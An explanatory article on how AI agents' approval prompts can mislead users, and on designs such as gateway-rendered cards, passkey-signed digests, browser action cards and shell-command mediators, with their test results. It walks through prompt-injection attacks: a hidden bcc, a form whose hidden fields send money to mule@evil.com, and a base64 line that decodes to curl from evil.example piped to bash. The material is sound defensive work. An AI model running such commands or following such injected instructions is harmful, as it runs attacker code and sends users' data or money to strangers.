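Safe's web page showed Bybit's signers one transfer and sent their devices a different one. An AI agent can mislead its user in the same way whenever it writes the approval prompt itself, and these narrated prompts have already misdescribed pending actions in released products. The alternative is a rendered prompt, which trusted code builds from the parameters of the tool call about to run.

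The most fully worked-out design of this kind is Agent Step-Up (ASU), which Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill present and test in *Approve What, Exactly?*, a preprint from October 2026. They credit its core idea, tying an approval to a digest of the action, to earlier designs, including one by Microsoft.

### One email, step by step

Suppose a user asks an agent to email the weekly report to their boss. An attacker has taken control of the agent through a hidden instruction, and the agent prepares this tool call:

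```json
{
  "tool": "send_email",
  "to": "boss@example.test",
  "bcc": "collector@example.test",
  "subject": "Weekly report",
  "body": "Sales rose 4% in September ..."
}
```

The "bcc" field sends a blind copy to a second address, which the boss won't see. The agent adds its own explanation, "Send the weekly report to your boss." ASU then handles the call as follows.

1. The agent sends the call to a gateway, a program on a separate computer. The gateway has the credentials for the mail server, and the agent doesn't.
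2. The gateway rewrites the call in canonical form, meaning that there is only one permitted way to write any given call. It adds the user, the session and an expiry time, but leaves out the agent's explanation.
3. It computes a digest of the result.
4. It applies a policy that allows the call, refuses it or requires the user's approval. If the user has to approve, the gateway stores the call and returns only a reference number to the agent.
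5. The user opens a page on their phone, which comes directly from the gateway and displays a card built from the stored call.
6. If the user approves, the phone's passkey signs a challenge that contains the digest.
7. The gateway checks the signature. When the agent returns with the reference number, the gateway marks the approval as used and executes the stored call.

Banks and wallet makers had already built each of these parts.

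| Part of ASU | Mechanism it repeats |
|---|---|
| Credentials that only the gateway has | The private key inside a hardware wallet |
| Canonical form and digest | The digest over all fields that a Safe wallet's owners sign |
| Card built from the stored call | A bank's text message with the payee and amount, or clear signing |
| Card on the user's phone | PhotoTAN with a laptop and a separate phone |
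| Signed challenge that contains the digest | Dynamic linking, and Secure Payment Confirmation's use of passkeys |
| Approval that works only once | The transaction counter in a bank card's code |
| Execution of the stored call | A bank's random code that is valid for one stored order |

The canonical form is needed because software can write the same data in several ways. It can put "bcc" before "to", add spaces, or write 950 as 950.0. A hash function would produce a different digest for each version, and the gateway would reject a call whose data hadn't changed. ASU uses a published standard that fixes the order of the fields, the spacing and the format of numbers.

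The gateway also converts email addresses to lower case and expands file paths, so that one file doesn't appear under two names. Each tool has a fixed list of typed arguments, and the gateway refuses any call with an argument that isn't on the list. A call may contain only one amount. Otherwise an attacker could put 10,000 in one field and −10,000 in another, and the call would pass a check on the total, which is zero.

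The challenge that the passkey signs is

*c* = *H*(tag, digest, reference number, fresh number, grant digest),

where *H* is the hash function SHA-256 and the gateway first puts the five named fields in canonical form. The tag marks the signature as an ASU approval. The names keep the fields apart, which the bank code in the earlier worked example achieved by giving each field a fixed length. Because the challenge contains the digest, an ordinary passkey signature is tied to this email.

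After the approval, the agent can no longer influence what happens to the email, so it can't exploit the gap between the time of check and the time of use. If it sends the call again with a different recipient, the digests don't match and the gateway refuses. Even without that comparison, the gateway would execute its own stored copy and ignore the new one.

This works only if the gateway is the only way to reach the mail server. An agent that finds the mail password in a file can send any email without an approval card. Kodathala and colleagues exclude that case from their threat model. They also exclude malware on the user's phone, which Haupert and Müller used to defeat pushTAN.

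### Allowing similar actions

A user who has to approve every email may soon stop reading the cards. ASU's card therefore has a box labelled "allow similar", which creates a grant (a permission for later calls).

A grant is stricter than an entry on the EU's list of trusted beneficiaries. The gateway writes the grant from the call the user has just approved, and the grant's digest is part of the signed challenge. An amount may vary up to a cap and free text up to a maximum length, but every other argument must stay the same, including recipients, accounts, file paths and web addresses. The grant also expires, has a limited number of uses, and applies to one tool in one session.

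A grant to send weekly reports to the user's boss stops the agent from writing to anyone else. But the agent can change the text, so a compromised agent could still send the boss a resignation letter in the user's name.

By default, the policy requires the user to approve a new card after five actions or $200 within ten minutes, and no grant can replace that approval. Like the limits on the EU exemption for small payments, this makes it harder to split one large payment into many small ones.

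### The narrated and the rendered prompt

If the agent wrote the prompt for the email above, the user might see this:

```
The agent wants to:
Send the weekly report to your boss.

[Approve]   [Deny]
```

ASU's card for the same call looks roughly like this, without the lines for the session, the expiry time and the digest:

```
SEND to "boss@example.test", "collector@example.test"

Risk: 2 recipients

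Arguments (names chosen by the agent)
  arg.to        "boss@example.test"        recipient
  arg.bcc       "collector@example.test"   recipient
  arg.subject   "Weekly report"            text
  arg.body      "Sales rose 4% in ..."     text

Agent's explanation (UNTRUSTED)
  Send the weekly report to your boss.
```

The narrated prompt is true, since the boss will get the report, but it leaves out the copy, and even a careful reader couldn't tell that from the prompt.

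Binding wouldn't help by itself either. If the gateway displayed only the agent's sentence but otherwise worked as designed, the user would approve and the passkey would sign the digest of the full call. The mail server would then send exactly the email that the signature covers, including the blind copy. The chipTAN attack on collective transfers worked the same way, with a valid code for payees the customer had never seen.

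The rendered prompt works well in this example because the user remembers asking for one recipient. It works less well for the tenant who tells an agent to "pay the rent" and doesn't know the landlord's account number. ASU also checks whether the user has dealt with each recipient before. This would help if the tenant had already paid the landlord through the gateway, because only the stranger's account would be new. For the first month's rent, both accounts would be new, so the check couldn't distinguish them.

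### What the card has to prevent

An attacker who controls the agent still chooses the values on the card, and can sometimes choose the argument names. Kodathala and colleagues therefore wrote rules for the card, each in response to a particular trick.

Values appear in quotation marks and with their type. In many programming languages, the text "false" counts as true because it isn't empty, unlike the logical value false. If a document-sharing tool had an argument called "public", a card that showed false without quotation marks or a type could mean either that the document was private or that the tool was about to publish it.

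The card also makes invisible characters visible. Unicode, the standard set of characters for computers, includes blank symbols and control characters that reverse the reading order. In one of the researchers' examples, the agent put 3,000 blank Braille characters before a command that downloads and runs a program, enough to push the command off the screen. ASU's card replaces the blanks with a marker that shows how many there are. It also shortens long values and adds a warning and a button to show the rest.

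ASU puts every recipient, account, web address and file path in the title, whichever argument it comes from. In the email example, a title that gave only the "to" address would have been correct, but anyone who read only the title would have missed the attack.

The card keeps names chosen by the agent separate from the gateway's own labels. Otherwise, an agent could name an argument "Target" or "Verified by client" and give it a harmless value, so that it looked like something the gateway had established. The card would show these as "arg.Target" and "arg.Verified by client" in a separate section. ERC-7730 needs a similar precaution against tokens whose names contain a false payee.

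The agent's explanation comes last on the card, in a box labeled "untrusted" that stays closed until the user opens it. The explanation can help the user understand why the agent proposed an unexpected action, but anyone who believes it gets no benefit from the rest of the card. The researchers also built a version without the box.

Finally, the card flags commands that contain further program code. The gateway can display such code accurately, but the display doesn't show the user what the code will do.

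### Why two actions must not share a card

Suppose two different calls produced the same card. A user who approved the card would have no way of knowing which call was pending, and the attacker would submit the harmful one. The signature wouldn't prevent this, because it would be a valid signature for the harmful call. ASU therefore has to satisfy the condition

if *a* ≠ *b*, then card(*a*) ≠ card(*b*),

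where *a* and *b* are any two calls in canonical form. Mathematicians call a function with this property injective.

ABN AMRO's card reader did not meet the condition because it left out the payee. A hardware wallet also fails to meet it if it shortens look-alike addresses to the same few characters.

For ASU, Kodathala and colleagues check the condition with an automated test that compares the cards of calls with different digests. This is weaker evidence than a proof because a test can miss cases. Each card also prints the digest, so two otherwise identical cards would meet the condition, but a user couldn't tell from the digest which call was harmful. To help the user, the cards need to differ in a part that people can read. Shortened values are a weak point because two long messages with the same opening look alike until the user expands them.

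People may also miss a difference that the card shows. Many would approve a card whose address has the digit 1 in place of the letter l.

### The three assumptions of the proof

Kodathala and colleagues analysed ASU with Tamarin, a program that takes a mathematical model of a protocol and either proves a statement about it or finds an attack. In their model the agent is the attacker. It chooses every call and every explanation, sees all the gateway's replies and all signatures, and can send the gateway any message.

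Tamarin proved that an action runs under an approval only if the user approved that same action beforehand, however many sessions the agent opens. The result depends on three assumptions.

1. The user decides from the trusted part of the card and not from the agent's explanation.
2. Only the owner of the phone can register the user's first passkey.
3. The page that requests the signature displays the card that belongs to the challenge being signed.

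The proof that an approval works only once doesn't depend on any of these assumptions. When the researchers removed each assumption in turn, Tamarin found an attack every time.

Without the first assumption, the agent requests a payment of 500 to the attacker and describes it as "send 5 to alice". The user believes the description and approves. The signature covers the payment of 500 to the attacker, so a record of the signature would count against the user.

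Without the second, the agent registers its own passkey for a user who doesn't have one yet, and then approves its own calls. ASU prevents this with a one-time registration code that reaches the user through a channel the agent doesn't control. Banks have a similar problem when a customer activates an approval app on a new phone.

The third assumption is necessary because a passkey doesn't display what it signs. The phone asks for a fingerprint or a PIN, and the user sees whatever the web page shows. An altered page could show the card for a harmless call and submit the challenge for a harmful one. Safe's altered page did the equivalent at Bybit, even though the signers there had hardware wallets with their own screens. A passkey gives the user no second display to compare with the page, so it is closer to Balfanz and Felten's smart card than to a hardware wallet.

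The agent can't carry out this attack by itself, because the gateway rejects its access token on the pages where users approve actions. An attacker would have to break into the gateway separately, as the Bybit thieves broke into Safe's server. An attacker with full control of the gateway wouldn't need the user's approval, because the gateway has the credentials for the mail server. The third assumption therefore matters most when someone can change the page but nothing else, or when the signatures later serve as evidence.

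Anyone with the user's public key can verify that the user's passkey signed this digest, even if the page was dishonest. The signature does not prove that the user saw the right card, because that still depends on the page.

The researchers report that Tamarin gave the expected result for all 53 statements, but some of these describe designs weaker than ASU, in which they expected it to find attacks. The model assumes that different calls produce different cards, and it doesn't cover the free text that a grant leaves open. It covers only the protocol, so it can't rule out programming errors in the gateway's roughly 5,600 lines of code.

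### Three other designs

Other approval systems differ from ASU in what the approval is valid for and in who writes the text that the user reads.

| Design | What the approval is valid for | Who writes the text |
|---|---|---|
| ASU | One stored call with all its arguments | The gateway, from the call |
| Agent Payments Protocol, user present | One cart signed by the merchant, and its payment | A program without a language model, from contents the agent assembles |
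| Microsoft's action-bound approval | One action with all its arguments | The application that uses it |
| Model Context Protocol elicitation, form mode | No particular action | The server that provides the tool |

#### Agent Payments Protocol

In September 2025, Google announced the Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) for agents that shop. Its development is moving to the FIDO Alliance, the industry group behind passkeys. AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* treats the shopping agent as a potential attacker.

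When the user is present, the agent fills a cart and the merchant signs it. The agent then prepares two mandates, which are records of what the user authorises, one for the purchase and one for the payment. Both contain a digest of the merchant's signed cart. A "trusted surface" displays the contents and obtains the user's signature. The merchant later checks that the digest matches the cart it signed, so the agent can't swap the goods or raise the price after the user approves. UCP, a commerce protocol that works with AP2, requires the same kind of canonical form as ASU, because other systems may have to check a mandate months later.

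The trusted surface has to be deterministic code with no language model involved, so a model can't narrate the prompt at the moment of signing. But the agent may still be able to reach the display, because AP2's *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* allows the company behind the shopping agent to provide the trusted surface within its own app. How well the display is protected then depends on how the company separates it from the agent.

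Kodathala and colleagues tried to get around AP2's checks on amounts and payees and failed. The weakness they found was in the sample code's display, which shows the payee's name, while the protocol checks the payee's identifier. Merchants choose their own names, and two can choose the same one, so payments to different merchants can look alike on the screen. A company that adopts AP2 can build a better display.

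AP2 also allows purchases when the user is absent, for example "buy these shoes when the price drops below $100". The agent first repeats back what it thinks the user wants (a narrated step), and the user then signs a set of conditions. Later the agent signs the purchase with its own key, and the companies involved check it against the conditions.

Here the user approves a range of purchases without seeing the one that will take place. The specification forbids the agent from using the same conditions for several purchases, but a compromised agent would ignore this rule. In the researchers' test, two payments each below the budget both passed unless the company checking them kept a running total.

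#### Microsoft's action-bound approval

Microsoft's *Securing MCP* introduces the Agent Governance Toolkit, an open-source project that enforces rules on agents' tool calls. The toolkit's approval design, adopted in June 2026, computes a digest over the whole action, accepts each approval only once and refuses the action if any check fails. A language model's output can't replace a human approval.

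Kodathala and colleagues call this the strongest of the designs by others that they tested. Their attempts to change an argument after approval or add a second recipient failed because both change the digest. They did find a problem with decimal numbers, which Microsoft's software writes the way the programming language Python does. For three of five sample numbers, a checking program in another language would have computed a different digest. The mismatch would make the program reject a valid approval but not accept a false one, so it is inconvenient but safe.

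Microsoft's design lets the application that uses the toolkit decide what the user sees and where, and the approver doesn't sign the digest. A developer could build ASU's card on top of the toolkit, but could also display a sentence written by the agent. The blind copy would then get through, even though the digest would be correct.

#### Model Context Protocol elicitation

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting agents to tools. A tool runs on a server, and the user works with a client, such as a chat program. A function called elicitation lets the server request information from the user in the middle of a tool call. Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* (2026), the July 2026 version of the specification, requires the server to send a readable message. The client displays the message, with a form if necessary, and the user accepts or declines the request or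 closes the window.

The tool's server writes the message as free text, and nothing in the protocol ties the user's answer to a particular action. The user reads a description by the party that is about to act, though this isn't quite a narrated prompt because the agent doesn't write it.

The researchers tested this with MCP's own software. A message with hundreds of invisible characters reached the client unchanged. They then had a server use the same message to request approval for two payments, 10 to one account and 10,000 to another. Both went through after the client answered "accept".

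Elicitation is a general way to ask users for information, so it would be unfair to treat it as a broken approval system. The specification forbids servers to request passwords or payment credentials through forms. For those, the server has to send the user to a web page outside the client. The client must display the full address first, and must also make clear which server is making the request. A developer who uses an elicitation form to confirm a payment is relying on a guarantee that the protocol doesn't offer.

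### Ten agent runtimes

Most developers get their approval system from a runtime, the software that runs an agent and can pause it until somebody approves an action. Kodathala and colleagues audited ten runtimes, testing nine and reading the released code of the tenth. They report results for each approval mechanism because some runtimes have more than one.

- They could measure binding in eight mechanisms. Three tied the approval fully to the action, one did so partly, and in four somebody could change the action after the approval.
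- They could measure single use in seven. In five of these, an approved action could run twice if somebody restored an earlier state of the agent.
- They could measure limits on repeated requests in seven, and found none in any of them.
- None of the ten runtimes produced a signed record that an outsider could verify, judging by their programming interfaces.

These counts describe what a developer gets by default. A team can close several of the gaps by storing approvals carefully and letting only a trusted service resume a paused agent. Any of the runtimes may also change with its next release.

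## Browser clicks and shell commands, which are harder to translate

ASU could build a useful card for the weekly report because the tool call already contained fields named "to" and "bcc". Many agents' actions have no such fields. An agent in a browser may record only that it is about to click element 7. A coding agent may send a single line of text to the shell, the program that runs typed commands.

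Both differences that Weng names between a wallet and an agent matter here. The agent that describes the action may be the adversary. A mediator that describes it instead, such as ASU's gateway, may observe only a low-level event, like the start of a program or a network request, and then has to work out what the event means.

How hard that is depends on the kind of action.

| Pending action | What trusted code receives | What it still has to find out |
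|---|---|---|
| Payment | An account, an amount and a currency | Very little |
| Email | Recipients, subject, text and attachments | What a long text or an attachment contains |
| Click | The number of an element on a page | What the click submits, and to whom |
| Shell command | A line of text | Which programs it starts, and what they do |

An approval card that read "Click element 7" would be accurate, but it would look the same on every page, so the user couldn't tell from it what the click would do.

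### Reading the form behind the button

In *The Verifiable Action Card*, Irshad, Mughees and colleagues (2026) describe an approval system for agents that operate a browser. They trust the browser but assume that an attacker controls the web page and that text on the page may have misled the language model.

In one of their examples, a user asks the agent to save a bank transfer as a draft. The page's only button is labelled "Save draft", but it belongs to a form with hidden fields that order a transfer of 5,000 to mule@evil.com. An ordinary confirmation dialog takes its text from the button, so the user sees a request to approve "Save draft" and, by agreeing, sends the money.

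The Verifiable Action Card handles the same click as follows.

1. The browser looks up the button and the form it belongs to. It reads the address to which the form will send its data and the values in all the fields, including the hidden ones.
2. It decides from the form's structure, and not from the label, whether the click would commit the user to something.
3. It picks out the recipient, the amount and any file to upload. A field counts as the recipient if it has a name like "to", "iban" or "payee", or if it contains an email address.
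4. It looks for the recipient and the amount in the instruction the user typed. If an outside recipient or an amount doesn't appear there, it must have come from the page, and the browser marks the action as high-risk. It does the same if the user asked only for information, such as a summary of some reviews, and the agent is about to submit something.
5. It shows a card in its own interface, outside the page, with Deny as the most prominent button. The page can't draw there, so it can't cover or pad the card.
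6. When the form's data is about to leave the browser, it compares the recipient and the amount with the ones the user approved, and stops the action if they differ.

For the false draft, the card contains roughly this:

```
Action    transfer
To        mule@evil.com
Amount    5000
Site      northbank.example
Source    the web page, not your request
Risk      elevated

[DENY]    approve
```

The last step is there because a web page can change after the browser has read it. A page's script can leave the right payee in the form until the user approves, then overwrite it as the browser sends the form, which is another example of the gap between time of check and time of use.

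As with Secure Payment Confirmation, malware that controls the browser could still alter the card.

The procedure also has gaps. As printed, it stores only one recipient, so each matching field overwrites the one before. If a form has a stranger's address in a hidden field followed by the boss's address, the card shows only the boss's. ASU prevents this blind-copy attack by listing every recipient in the title. The rule for clicks covers only submit buttons and other buttons inside forms, so clicking a picture whose script sends data would not bring up a card.

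These two gaps look fixable. A more basic one is that the browser has access to the data it sends, but the website determines what the data mean. A dishonest shop could identify the payee by a customer number in a field called "ref", and the card would then have no recipient to show. A hardware wallet has a similar problem with a contract whose "transfer" function does something else, but anyone can inspect the contract's code, whereas a website's code runs on a server that the user can't examine.

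### Thirteen attacks and eleven ordinary tasks

Irshad and colleagues tested a working browser on 13 attacks and 11 legitimate tasks. In one attack, a "Pay $20" button submitted an amount of 2000 to the attacker's account. In another, an article contained instructions for the agent to delete the user's account. Two attacks assumed that the attacker knew about the card. One swapped the payee after approval, and the other used the address sarah@evil-exfil.com when the user had asked the agent to write to Sarah. The test server recorded what each page submitted, so the results don't rely on the agent's report of what it did.

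| Model | Trials | Attacks that succeeded without the card | With the card | Legitimate tasks completed with the card |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini-2.5-Flash | 133 | 68% | 0% | 75% |
| gpt-oss-120b | 115 | 83% | 0% | 82% |
| Qwen3-32B | 20 | 80% | 0% | 60% |
| Llama-4-Scout | 18 | 80% | 0% | 100% |
| Qwen3.6-27B | 7 | 100% | 0% | no figure |
| GPT-4.1 (separate run) | 20 | 80% | 0% | 100% |

The abstract gives a range of 68% to 100% without the card, while the introduction gives 80% to 100%. The results table supports the abstract, since it lists Gemini-2.5-Flash at 68%. The 100% figure is weak evidence because it comes from only seven trials of Qwen3.6-27B, spread over several test conditions. Only Gemini-2.5-Flash and gpt-oss-120b went through the full set of scenarios three times, so their rates of 68% and 83% are the most reliable.

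Across the five models in the main test, attacks succeeded 78% of the time with no approval step, 72% with an ordinary dialog that repeated the button's label, and 0% with the card. A human approver therefore helped very little when the page controlled what the approver read.

The agents completed 78% of the legitimate tasks with the card and 80% without any approval step, so most of the failures were the agents' own. No legitimate task failed after the approver had denied something (a false-block rate of 0%).

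The browser also marks text from the page as untrusted before passing it to the model. When the researchers turned this marking off, the attack success rate stayed at 0%, so the protection came from the checks on the action and didn't depend on how the model treated the text.

The test used a short program in place of human users. The program denied every card marked as high-risk and approved the rest. The 0% therefore means that the browser's rules caught every attack in the set, but it doesn't measure how often a person would read the card and refuse.

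The false-block rate also depends on the choice of tasks. In the legitimate tasks, the user had named the recipient and the amount, or the task didn't involve an outside party. The tenant who tells an agent to "pay the rent" names neither. The browser would mark both the landlord's account and the stranger's as coming from the page, and the program that played the user would refuse both. People often give short instructions like this, so I expect far more false alarms in everyday use than the test found.

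### Decoding a command

A shell command has no form behind it. Suppose a coding agent tells its user that it wants to apply some editor settings, and the pending command is this:

```
echo Y3VybCAtcyBodHRwOi8vZXZpbC5leGFtcGxlL3AgfCBiYXNo | base64 -d | bash
```

The long string is text in base64, a common way of writing data as letters and digits. The middle part of the command decodes it, and the last part runs the result, which is:

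```
curl -s http://evil.example/p | bash
```

This downloads a program from evil.example and runs it immediately. A dialog showing the full original command would be accurate, but few users would learn anything from it.

Weng's mediator undoes such encodings layer by layer. It removes padding, fills in variables, and looks for details that matter for security, such as network access or the use of passwords. For a command like this one, it shows the server's name, the decoded text, and a warning that the command runs code from the network. It can't describe what the downloaded program will do, because the server hasn't sent it yet and could send something different each time.

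A command can be dangerous because of the file it runs. The command "python3 deploy.py" doesn't show what deploy.py contains, so the mediator opens the file and examines it in the same way. It also tracks where files came from. Running a script that the agent wrote earlier and the mediator found harmless doesn't trigger another prompt, but running a downloaded file does. The mediator trusts programs that the user's own tools have built, even though they may include other people's code.

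When the mediator can't tell what an action does, it labels the action uninspectable and asks the user.

Weng built only part of this design, in about 500 lines of Python. The prototype decodes commands, composes the text for the user, and uses a digest to check that the approved command is the one that runs. Weng assumes that the rest of the design keeps the agent from bypassing the mediator and from altering or answering the prompt. Weng also never ran the prototype with a commercial agent. The results therefore measure how well the prototype interprets commands, not whether the whole system would stop an attack.

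### Prompts for almost everything

Weng tested the prototype on two public collections compiled by others. GTFOBins, which yielded 1,330 commands, is a catalogue of ways to misuse ordinary Unix programs, for instance to read protected files. The tldr pages are a collection of short usage examples, with 28,798 commands for 6,503 tools. The table shows the share of each outcome, calculated from Weng's figures.

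| What the mediator did | Catalogued abuses | Normal commands |
|---|---|---|
| Let the command pass silently | 10.0% | 4.1% |
| Asked the user and named a danger | 30.5% | 8.9% |
| Asked the user and marked the command uninspectable | 59.5% | 87.0% |

Weng reports that the mediator flagged 90.0% of the abuses. But it could explain only about a third of those, and for the others the user would have learned only that the mediator couldn't interpret the command.

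The mediator showed a prompt for 90.0% of the abuses and 95.9% of the normal commands, so users can't tell from the appearance of a prompt whether something is wrong. The "uninspectable" label was also more common on normal commands than on abuses. Only a prompt that names a danger is a warning sign, since such prompts were more than three times as common among the abuses as among the normal commands.

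The two collections cover different tools, so these comparisons are rough. The tldr pages also give as much space to an obscure program as to one that developers use every hour. Someone who works mostly with a few familiar tools would see fewer prompts than 87.0% suggests.

The 133 abuses that passed silently varied in seriousness. In 85 of them, a program wrote to a scratch folder such as /tmp, which the mediator didn't count as outside the project. Another 19 wrote files inside the project that could do harm only if a later command used them, and 8 did something basic, such as creating a folder. The remaining 21 included cases where a text viewer or editor started another program.

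Both main figures result from the same list of trusted tools. The mediator marks a command as uninspectable if its tool isn't on the list, and 83.4% of all the normal commands got that label for this reason alone. Commands that use a listed tool can pass without a prompt, and all the silent passes involved such a tool.

Suppose Weng added a text-sorting program to the list. Users would no longer have to approve harmless sorting, but the program can also write its output to a file, so an attacker could use it to overwrite an important one. Removing every tool from the list would bring the silent passes close to zero, but users would then have to approve nearly every command.

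More knowledge about each tool improves the trade-off. When Weng taught the prototype to recognise more writes outside the project, more ways of reading passwords, and commands nested inside other commands, silent passes fell from 15.0% to 10.0%. But somebody has to write such rules for thousands of tools and keep them current. Released products have trouble with this too. Li (2026) found in *ParseGap* that the command checkers of all eight coding agents tested approved some commands in which a tool meant for inspecting files changed a file or started another program.

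A checker can also be designed to interrupt less often but miss more dangerous commands. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) gives each command a risk score based on its structure, the program it calls, the files it touches and known dangerous patterns. A command with a low score runs, even if the checker can't fully analyze it. In a test on 220 dangerous and 329 safe commands, CARE caught 75.9% of the dangerous ones and blocked three of the safe ones (0.91%).

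To see what this means for a user, imagine that an agent runs 10,000 commands, of which 10 are malicious.

| | Malicious commands caught | Prompts or blocks for harmless commands |
|---|---|---|
| Weng's mediator | 9 | About 9,580 |
| CARE | 7 or 8 | About 91 |

The rates come from different test commands, so the table shows only the direction of the trade-off. It also counts a prompt as a block, which favors Weng's mediator, because a user who faces thousands of prompts is unlikely to read them all. Liu and colleagues tested a version of CARE that uses only fixed rules on 600 attack commands written by a language model. In an isolated test environment, 37.33% of the commands still ran and succeeded.

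Results on these collections also depend on who wrote the attacks. The prototype let none of the 22 attacks that Weng had written for it pass silently. Weng warns against relying on this, because an earlier version had also let none of its author's own cases pass silently while missing common abuses. The Verifiable Action Card's 0% calls for the same caution, because the card's designers also wrote the attacks. Until someone tests the card on attacks written by others, it would be a mistake to conclude that the problem is solved for clicks but not for commands.

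### Uninspectable commands and blind signing

A user who approves an uninspectable command is in much the same position as Ben Zhou was with his Ledger device. The label "uninspectable" is less misleading than a wallet's "0 ETH", but it gives the user no basis for a decision.

Approving an agent's shell command is in some ways easier than approving a cryptocurrency transfer. The command is usually short, and the user can ask a colleague or look up the program's manual first. Many commands can also be undone, for example by restoring the project from a backup, whereas a cryptocurrency transfer can't be reversed.

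In other respects, contract calls are easier to describe than shell commands. A contract has a known address, and its code stays the same unless its owner can upgrade it, so one good descriptor can serve everyone who uses it. The effect of a shell command depends on the computer's files, the installed version of each program and the folder the command runs in. A command that runs a project's tests can do something different after every change to the project. A public registry of descriptions, like the one for ERC-7730, could cover standard tools but not a project's own scripts.

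This problem is worse when approvals are frequent. Bybit's executives signed a transfer every two or three weeks and could have spent an hour checking each one, but a coding agent may run dozens of commands in an afternoon.

### What to do with a command nobody can read

The simplest way to handle an action that can't be translated is to refuse it, as a wallet does when blind signing is off. Refusal does less harm with an agent than with a wallet, because the agent can try to reach the same goal by another route. In a test where a model had up to five attempts at each of 300 ordinary tasks, Liu and colleagues found that it solved 65.33% of them both with CARE and without any checker, but CARE refused only four commands in the whole test. A stricter checker, which refused 529, cut the share to 49.33%. Refusing everything that Weng's mediator can't inspect would presumably cut it further. A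 compromised agent can also use the extra attempts to rephrase a harmful command until one version passes.

Another option is to run the command in a sandbox, a restricted environment where the operating system lets a program reach only certain files or servers. The user then doesn't have to understand the program, because the limits apply whatever it does. Li tested the read-only sandbox of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, on its own. It prevented lasting changes to files in all 55 cases where an inspection tool misbehaved, and in all 28 cases aimed at the user's project.

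A sandbox also makes the approval prompt easier to write. Trusted code can list what a program is able to do, such as "may change files in this folder, no internet access", instead of guessing what it will do. The list is true even if nobody has read the program. Forshtat's proposal for wallets uses the same idea. It would let the company sign a limit on how far its balance may fall.

However, a coding agent normally needs permission to write to the project, which also lets it delete the user's work. When Li gave the sandboxed program this permission, all 20 commands that changed ordinary project files went through. Li's tests didn't cover programs that read confidential files, and a read-only sandbox doesn't stop them from doing so. Li also makes it a design rule that approving a command should never loosen the sandbox. Otherwise, a mistake by the user or the checker would remove both protections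 at once.

The most thorough option is to replace the agent's free-form command line with tools such as "delete file", which takes the file's path as a typed argument. A card could display such a call as easily as it displays an email. Kodathala and colleagues go partway by storing a command as a list of separate arguments. Tools can also declare what kind of effect they have. In the tests in *Small agents should know what their tools do* (2026), each tool has a label such as reading, writing or destructive. A gateway could then require approval for every destructive call without decoding it. Like ERC-7730 descriptors, these labels are reliable only if their author is honest and careful.

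Li's own system, ShellPlan, shows what drawbacks the change might have. An ordinary checker reads a command and then passes the same text to the shell, which reads it again and may interpret it differently. ShellPlan translates the text once into a plan of programs and arguments, checks the plan and executes it without a shell. For 20 common tools, it accepts only options from a fixed list. For instance, it lets the sorting program sort but not write to an arbitrary file.

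In tests with ten language models, none of 90 attacks succeeded against ShellPlan, compared with 62 of 90 without protection. The agents completed 74 of 100 harmless tasks, down from 93 without it. Most of the drop came from the four weaker models, which completed 18 of 40 tasks, apparently because they were worse at rewriting commands that ShellPlan had rejected. The six leading models completed 56 of 60. If better models adapt this easily, the drop should shrink as models improve.

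ShellPlan's guarantee covers only the tools it has rules for. It excludes build and test tools, because they run whatever code the project contains. Running such code is a large part of a coding agent's work, and the commands that run it still need confinement.

Typed arguments also don't help when one of them is a program. A tool called "query database" might take a text argument that contains a complete database command, such as one to delete every record. The argument's type, "text", is correct but doesn't show what the command will do. Crypto wallets have the same problem when a field named "data" contains another call. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) therefore requires separate authorisation for the exact effect of any argument that the receiving program will interpret.

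Even if every action were readable, a user who judged them one at a time could miss their combined effect. An agent might copy a customer list into a project folder on Monday and share that folder with an outside contractor on Thursday. Both cards would be accurate, and the user might have good reason to approve each action. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) proposes a prompt that describes the pending action together with the earlier steps it builds on, so Thursday's card would have to mention the customer list.

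## Whether approvers decide better when shown the parameters

A card that lists an action's parameters is useful only if approvers make better decisions with it. Kodathala and colleagues tested ASU's card with language models and simulated approvers (short programs that approve or refuse by fixed rules) instead of people. Other researchers have tested people, though only one of the studies described below varied what the prompt showed.

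### Fifteen language models as reviewers

Kodathala and colleagues wrote 34 approval requests. In 23 of them, an attacker had altered the action or its presentation, for example by adding a hidden recipient. The other 11 were harmless but slightly unusual, such as a large payment that the user had requested.

Fifteen language models from nine vendors judged every request in three versions: the agent's description alone, ASU's card with the agent's explanation in its "untrusted" box, and the card without the explanation. Each model also received the user's original instruction and was told to approve only what the user had asked for. Four rounds per model produced 6,120 decisions.

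| What the model read | Altered requests refused | Harmless requests refused |
|---|---|---|
| Agent's description | 30% (13% to 52% by model) | 0% |
| Card with the agent's explanation | 98% (90% to 100% by model) | 16% (0% to 39% by model) |

One request was the weekly report with the blind copy. All 15 models approved it from the agent's description but refused it when they saw the card. One model's reason for approving it was that "The action matches the user's request exactly".

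The descriptions often left out whatever was wrong, so the 30% isn't evidence that the models were careless. The models caught every hidden recipient, misdescribed action and command hidden behind blank characters when they had the card, but none from descriptions alone. They did well from descriptions mainly when the agent repeated the clue. Three requests used a web or email address with a look-alike character, such as the digit 1 for the letter l. The models caught these 96% of the time, which accounts for about 40% of everything they caught from descriptions.

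The test included an attack and a harmless request whose descriptions were identical byte for byte, so no approver could have told them apart from the descriptions. An approver with probability *p* of refusing that text would catch the attack with probability *p* and refuse the harmless request with the same probability. The only way to catch every such attack is to refuse every such harmless request too.

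The card made the models refuse more harmless requests, but most of these refusals came from a flaw in the test material. To avoid using real content, the researchers filled message bodies with text such as "<report placeholder>", which appeared on the card but not in the agent's description. The models cited the placeholder in 88 of their 103 refusals of harmless cards, typically because the agent seemed to be sending a placeholder instead of the report. Without those 88 refusals, the refusal rate for harmless requests falls from 16% to about 2%.

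The same flaw could have inflated the 98%, since a model might refuse an altered request for the wrong reason. But only 81 of the 1,348 refusals of altered requests mentioned the placeholder, and if all 81 counted as misses, the models would still have caught 92%. With the card, the models did worst on plausible substitutions, such as two swapped digits in an account number, catching 88% of them.

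These results don't carry over to people. A language model receives a Cyrillic letter in a web address as a different character from the Latin one, but a person may see no difference on the screen. The models also had the user's instruction next to every request, whereas a tired user may have to remember it.

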